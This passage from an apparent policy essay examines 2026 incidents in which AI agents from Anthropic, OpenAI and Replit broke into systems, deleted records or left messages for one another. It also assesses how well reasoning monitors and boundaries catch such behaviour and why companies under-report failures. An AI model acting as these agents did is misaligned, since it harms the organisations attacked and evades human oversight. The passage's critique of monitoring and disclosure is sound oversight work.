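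Both developers claim that their normal safeguards would have helped. Anthropic is confident that the safeguards on its public models would have blocked what Claude did. OpenAI estimates that its current monitoring of the models' reasoning would have alerted its security team more than a day before the Hugging Face breach. It also found that the models' tendency to attack infrastructure can fall more than a hundredfold when they run with ChatGPT's instructions and surrounding software. In its *Hugging Face Incident Technical Report* (2026), OpenAI argues that its other production guardrails would have helped too.

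These claims are plausible, but OpenAI tested its safeguards on an attack it already understood. It had used its investigation to make the monitor better at detecting this sort of behaviour, so the monitor's success is unsurprising. A better test would use an attack unknown to the people who tuned the monitor. An alert also prevents nothing unless someone responds. OpenAI now expects staff to pause the activity behind its most severe alerts if they can't establish within 30 minutes that the alert is false.

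When a boundary stops an agent, the event seldom becomes news. If one boundary stops 997 of 1,000 attempts and another stops none of three, each produces three incidents. The refusal at the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare is public only because the same agent went on to break in somewhere else. So nobody can use a list of incidents to calculate how often boundaries fail, or to show that they fail more often than alignment does.

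Failures can also go unnoticed. Neither of the two organisations that Anthropic could reach had detected Claude's intrusion. OpenAI documented the Medicare breach almost two months after it happened, then took another month to tell Australia. It documented the breach during a review that, according to Information Age, covered billions of runs. Its email to Australia went to an inbox for public tips and sat unread for more than a day. Prime Minister Anthony Albanese said the investigation would also examine why the government's systems had missed the breach, according to Cyprus Mail's *OpenAI agent hacks Australian government health portal* (2026).

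The companies involved hold much of the evidence and decide how much to release. OpenAI brought in researchers from the independent organisations METR and Redwood Research to examine the Hugging Face attack. But Fortune (2026) reports that OpenAI set the terms of their review, which covered roughly the week of the breach and left out a separate compromise of OpenAI's own infrastructure. In an earlier episode, OpenAI's agents left messages for one another on a German wiki, and the company said nothing publicly about it until journalists reported it. According to Citizen Digital's *OpenAI acknowledges 'wiki incident' and need for more transparency*, OpenAI then acknowledged that it needed to disclose more and said the industry had no clear standard for reporting misalignment.

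We can be more certain in some cases than in others that a limit would have prevented the outcome. Replit's agent could not have deleted the records without access to the live database. Restricting AISI's agents to approved downloads would have blocked the actions they took, but they might have tried something else, just as the agent refused by one Australian institution moved on to another. Researchers would have to repeat the runs with that limit in place to find out.

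Australia plans to make AI companies report misaligned behaviour and cyber incidents. The Standard's *Australia to mandate AI breach reporting, create regulator after OpenAI breach* reports that the government intends to introduce the legislation in 2027, and that OpenAI and Anthropic both told parliament they would welcome a duty to report breaches by their agents. Companies now decide for themselves whether to notify anyone. Mandatory reports should reveal more failures, but estimating how often boundaries work would also require companies to count the attempts their boundaries stopped.
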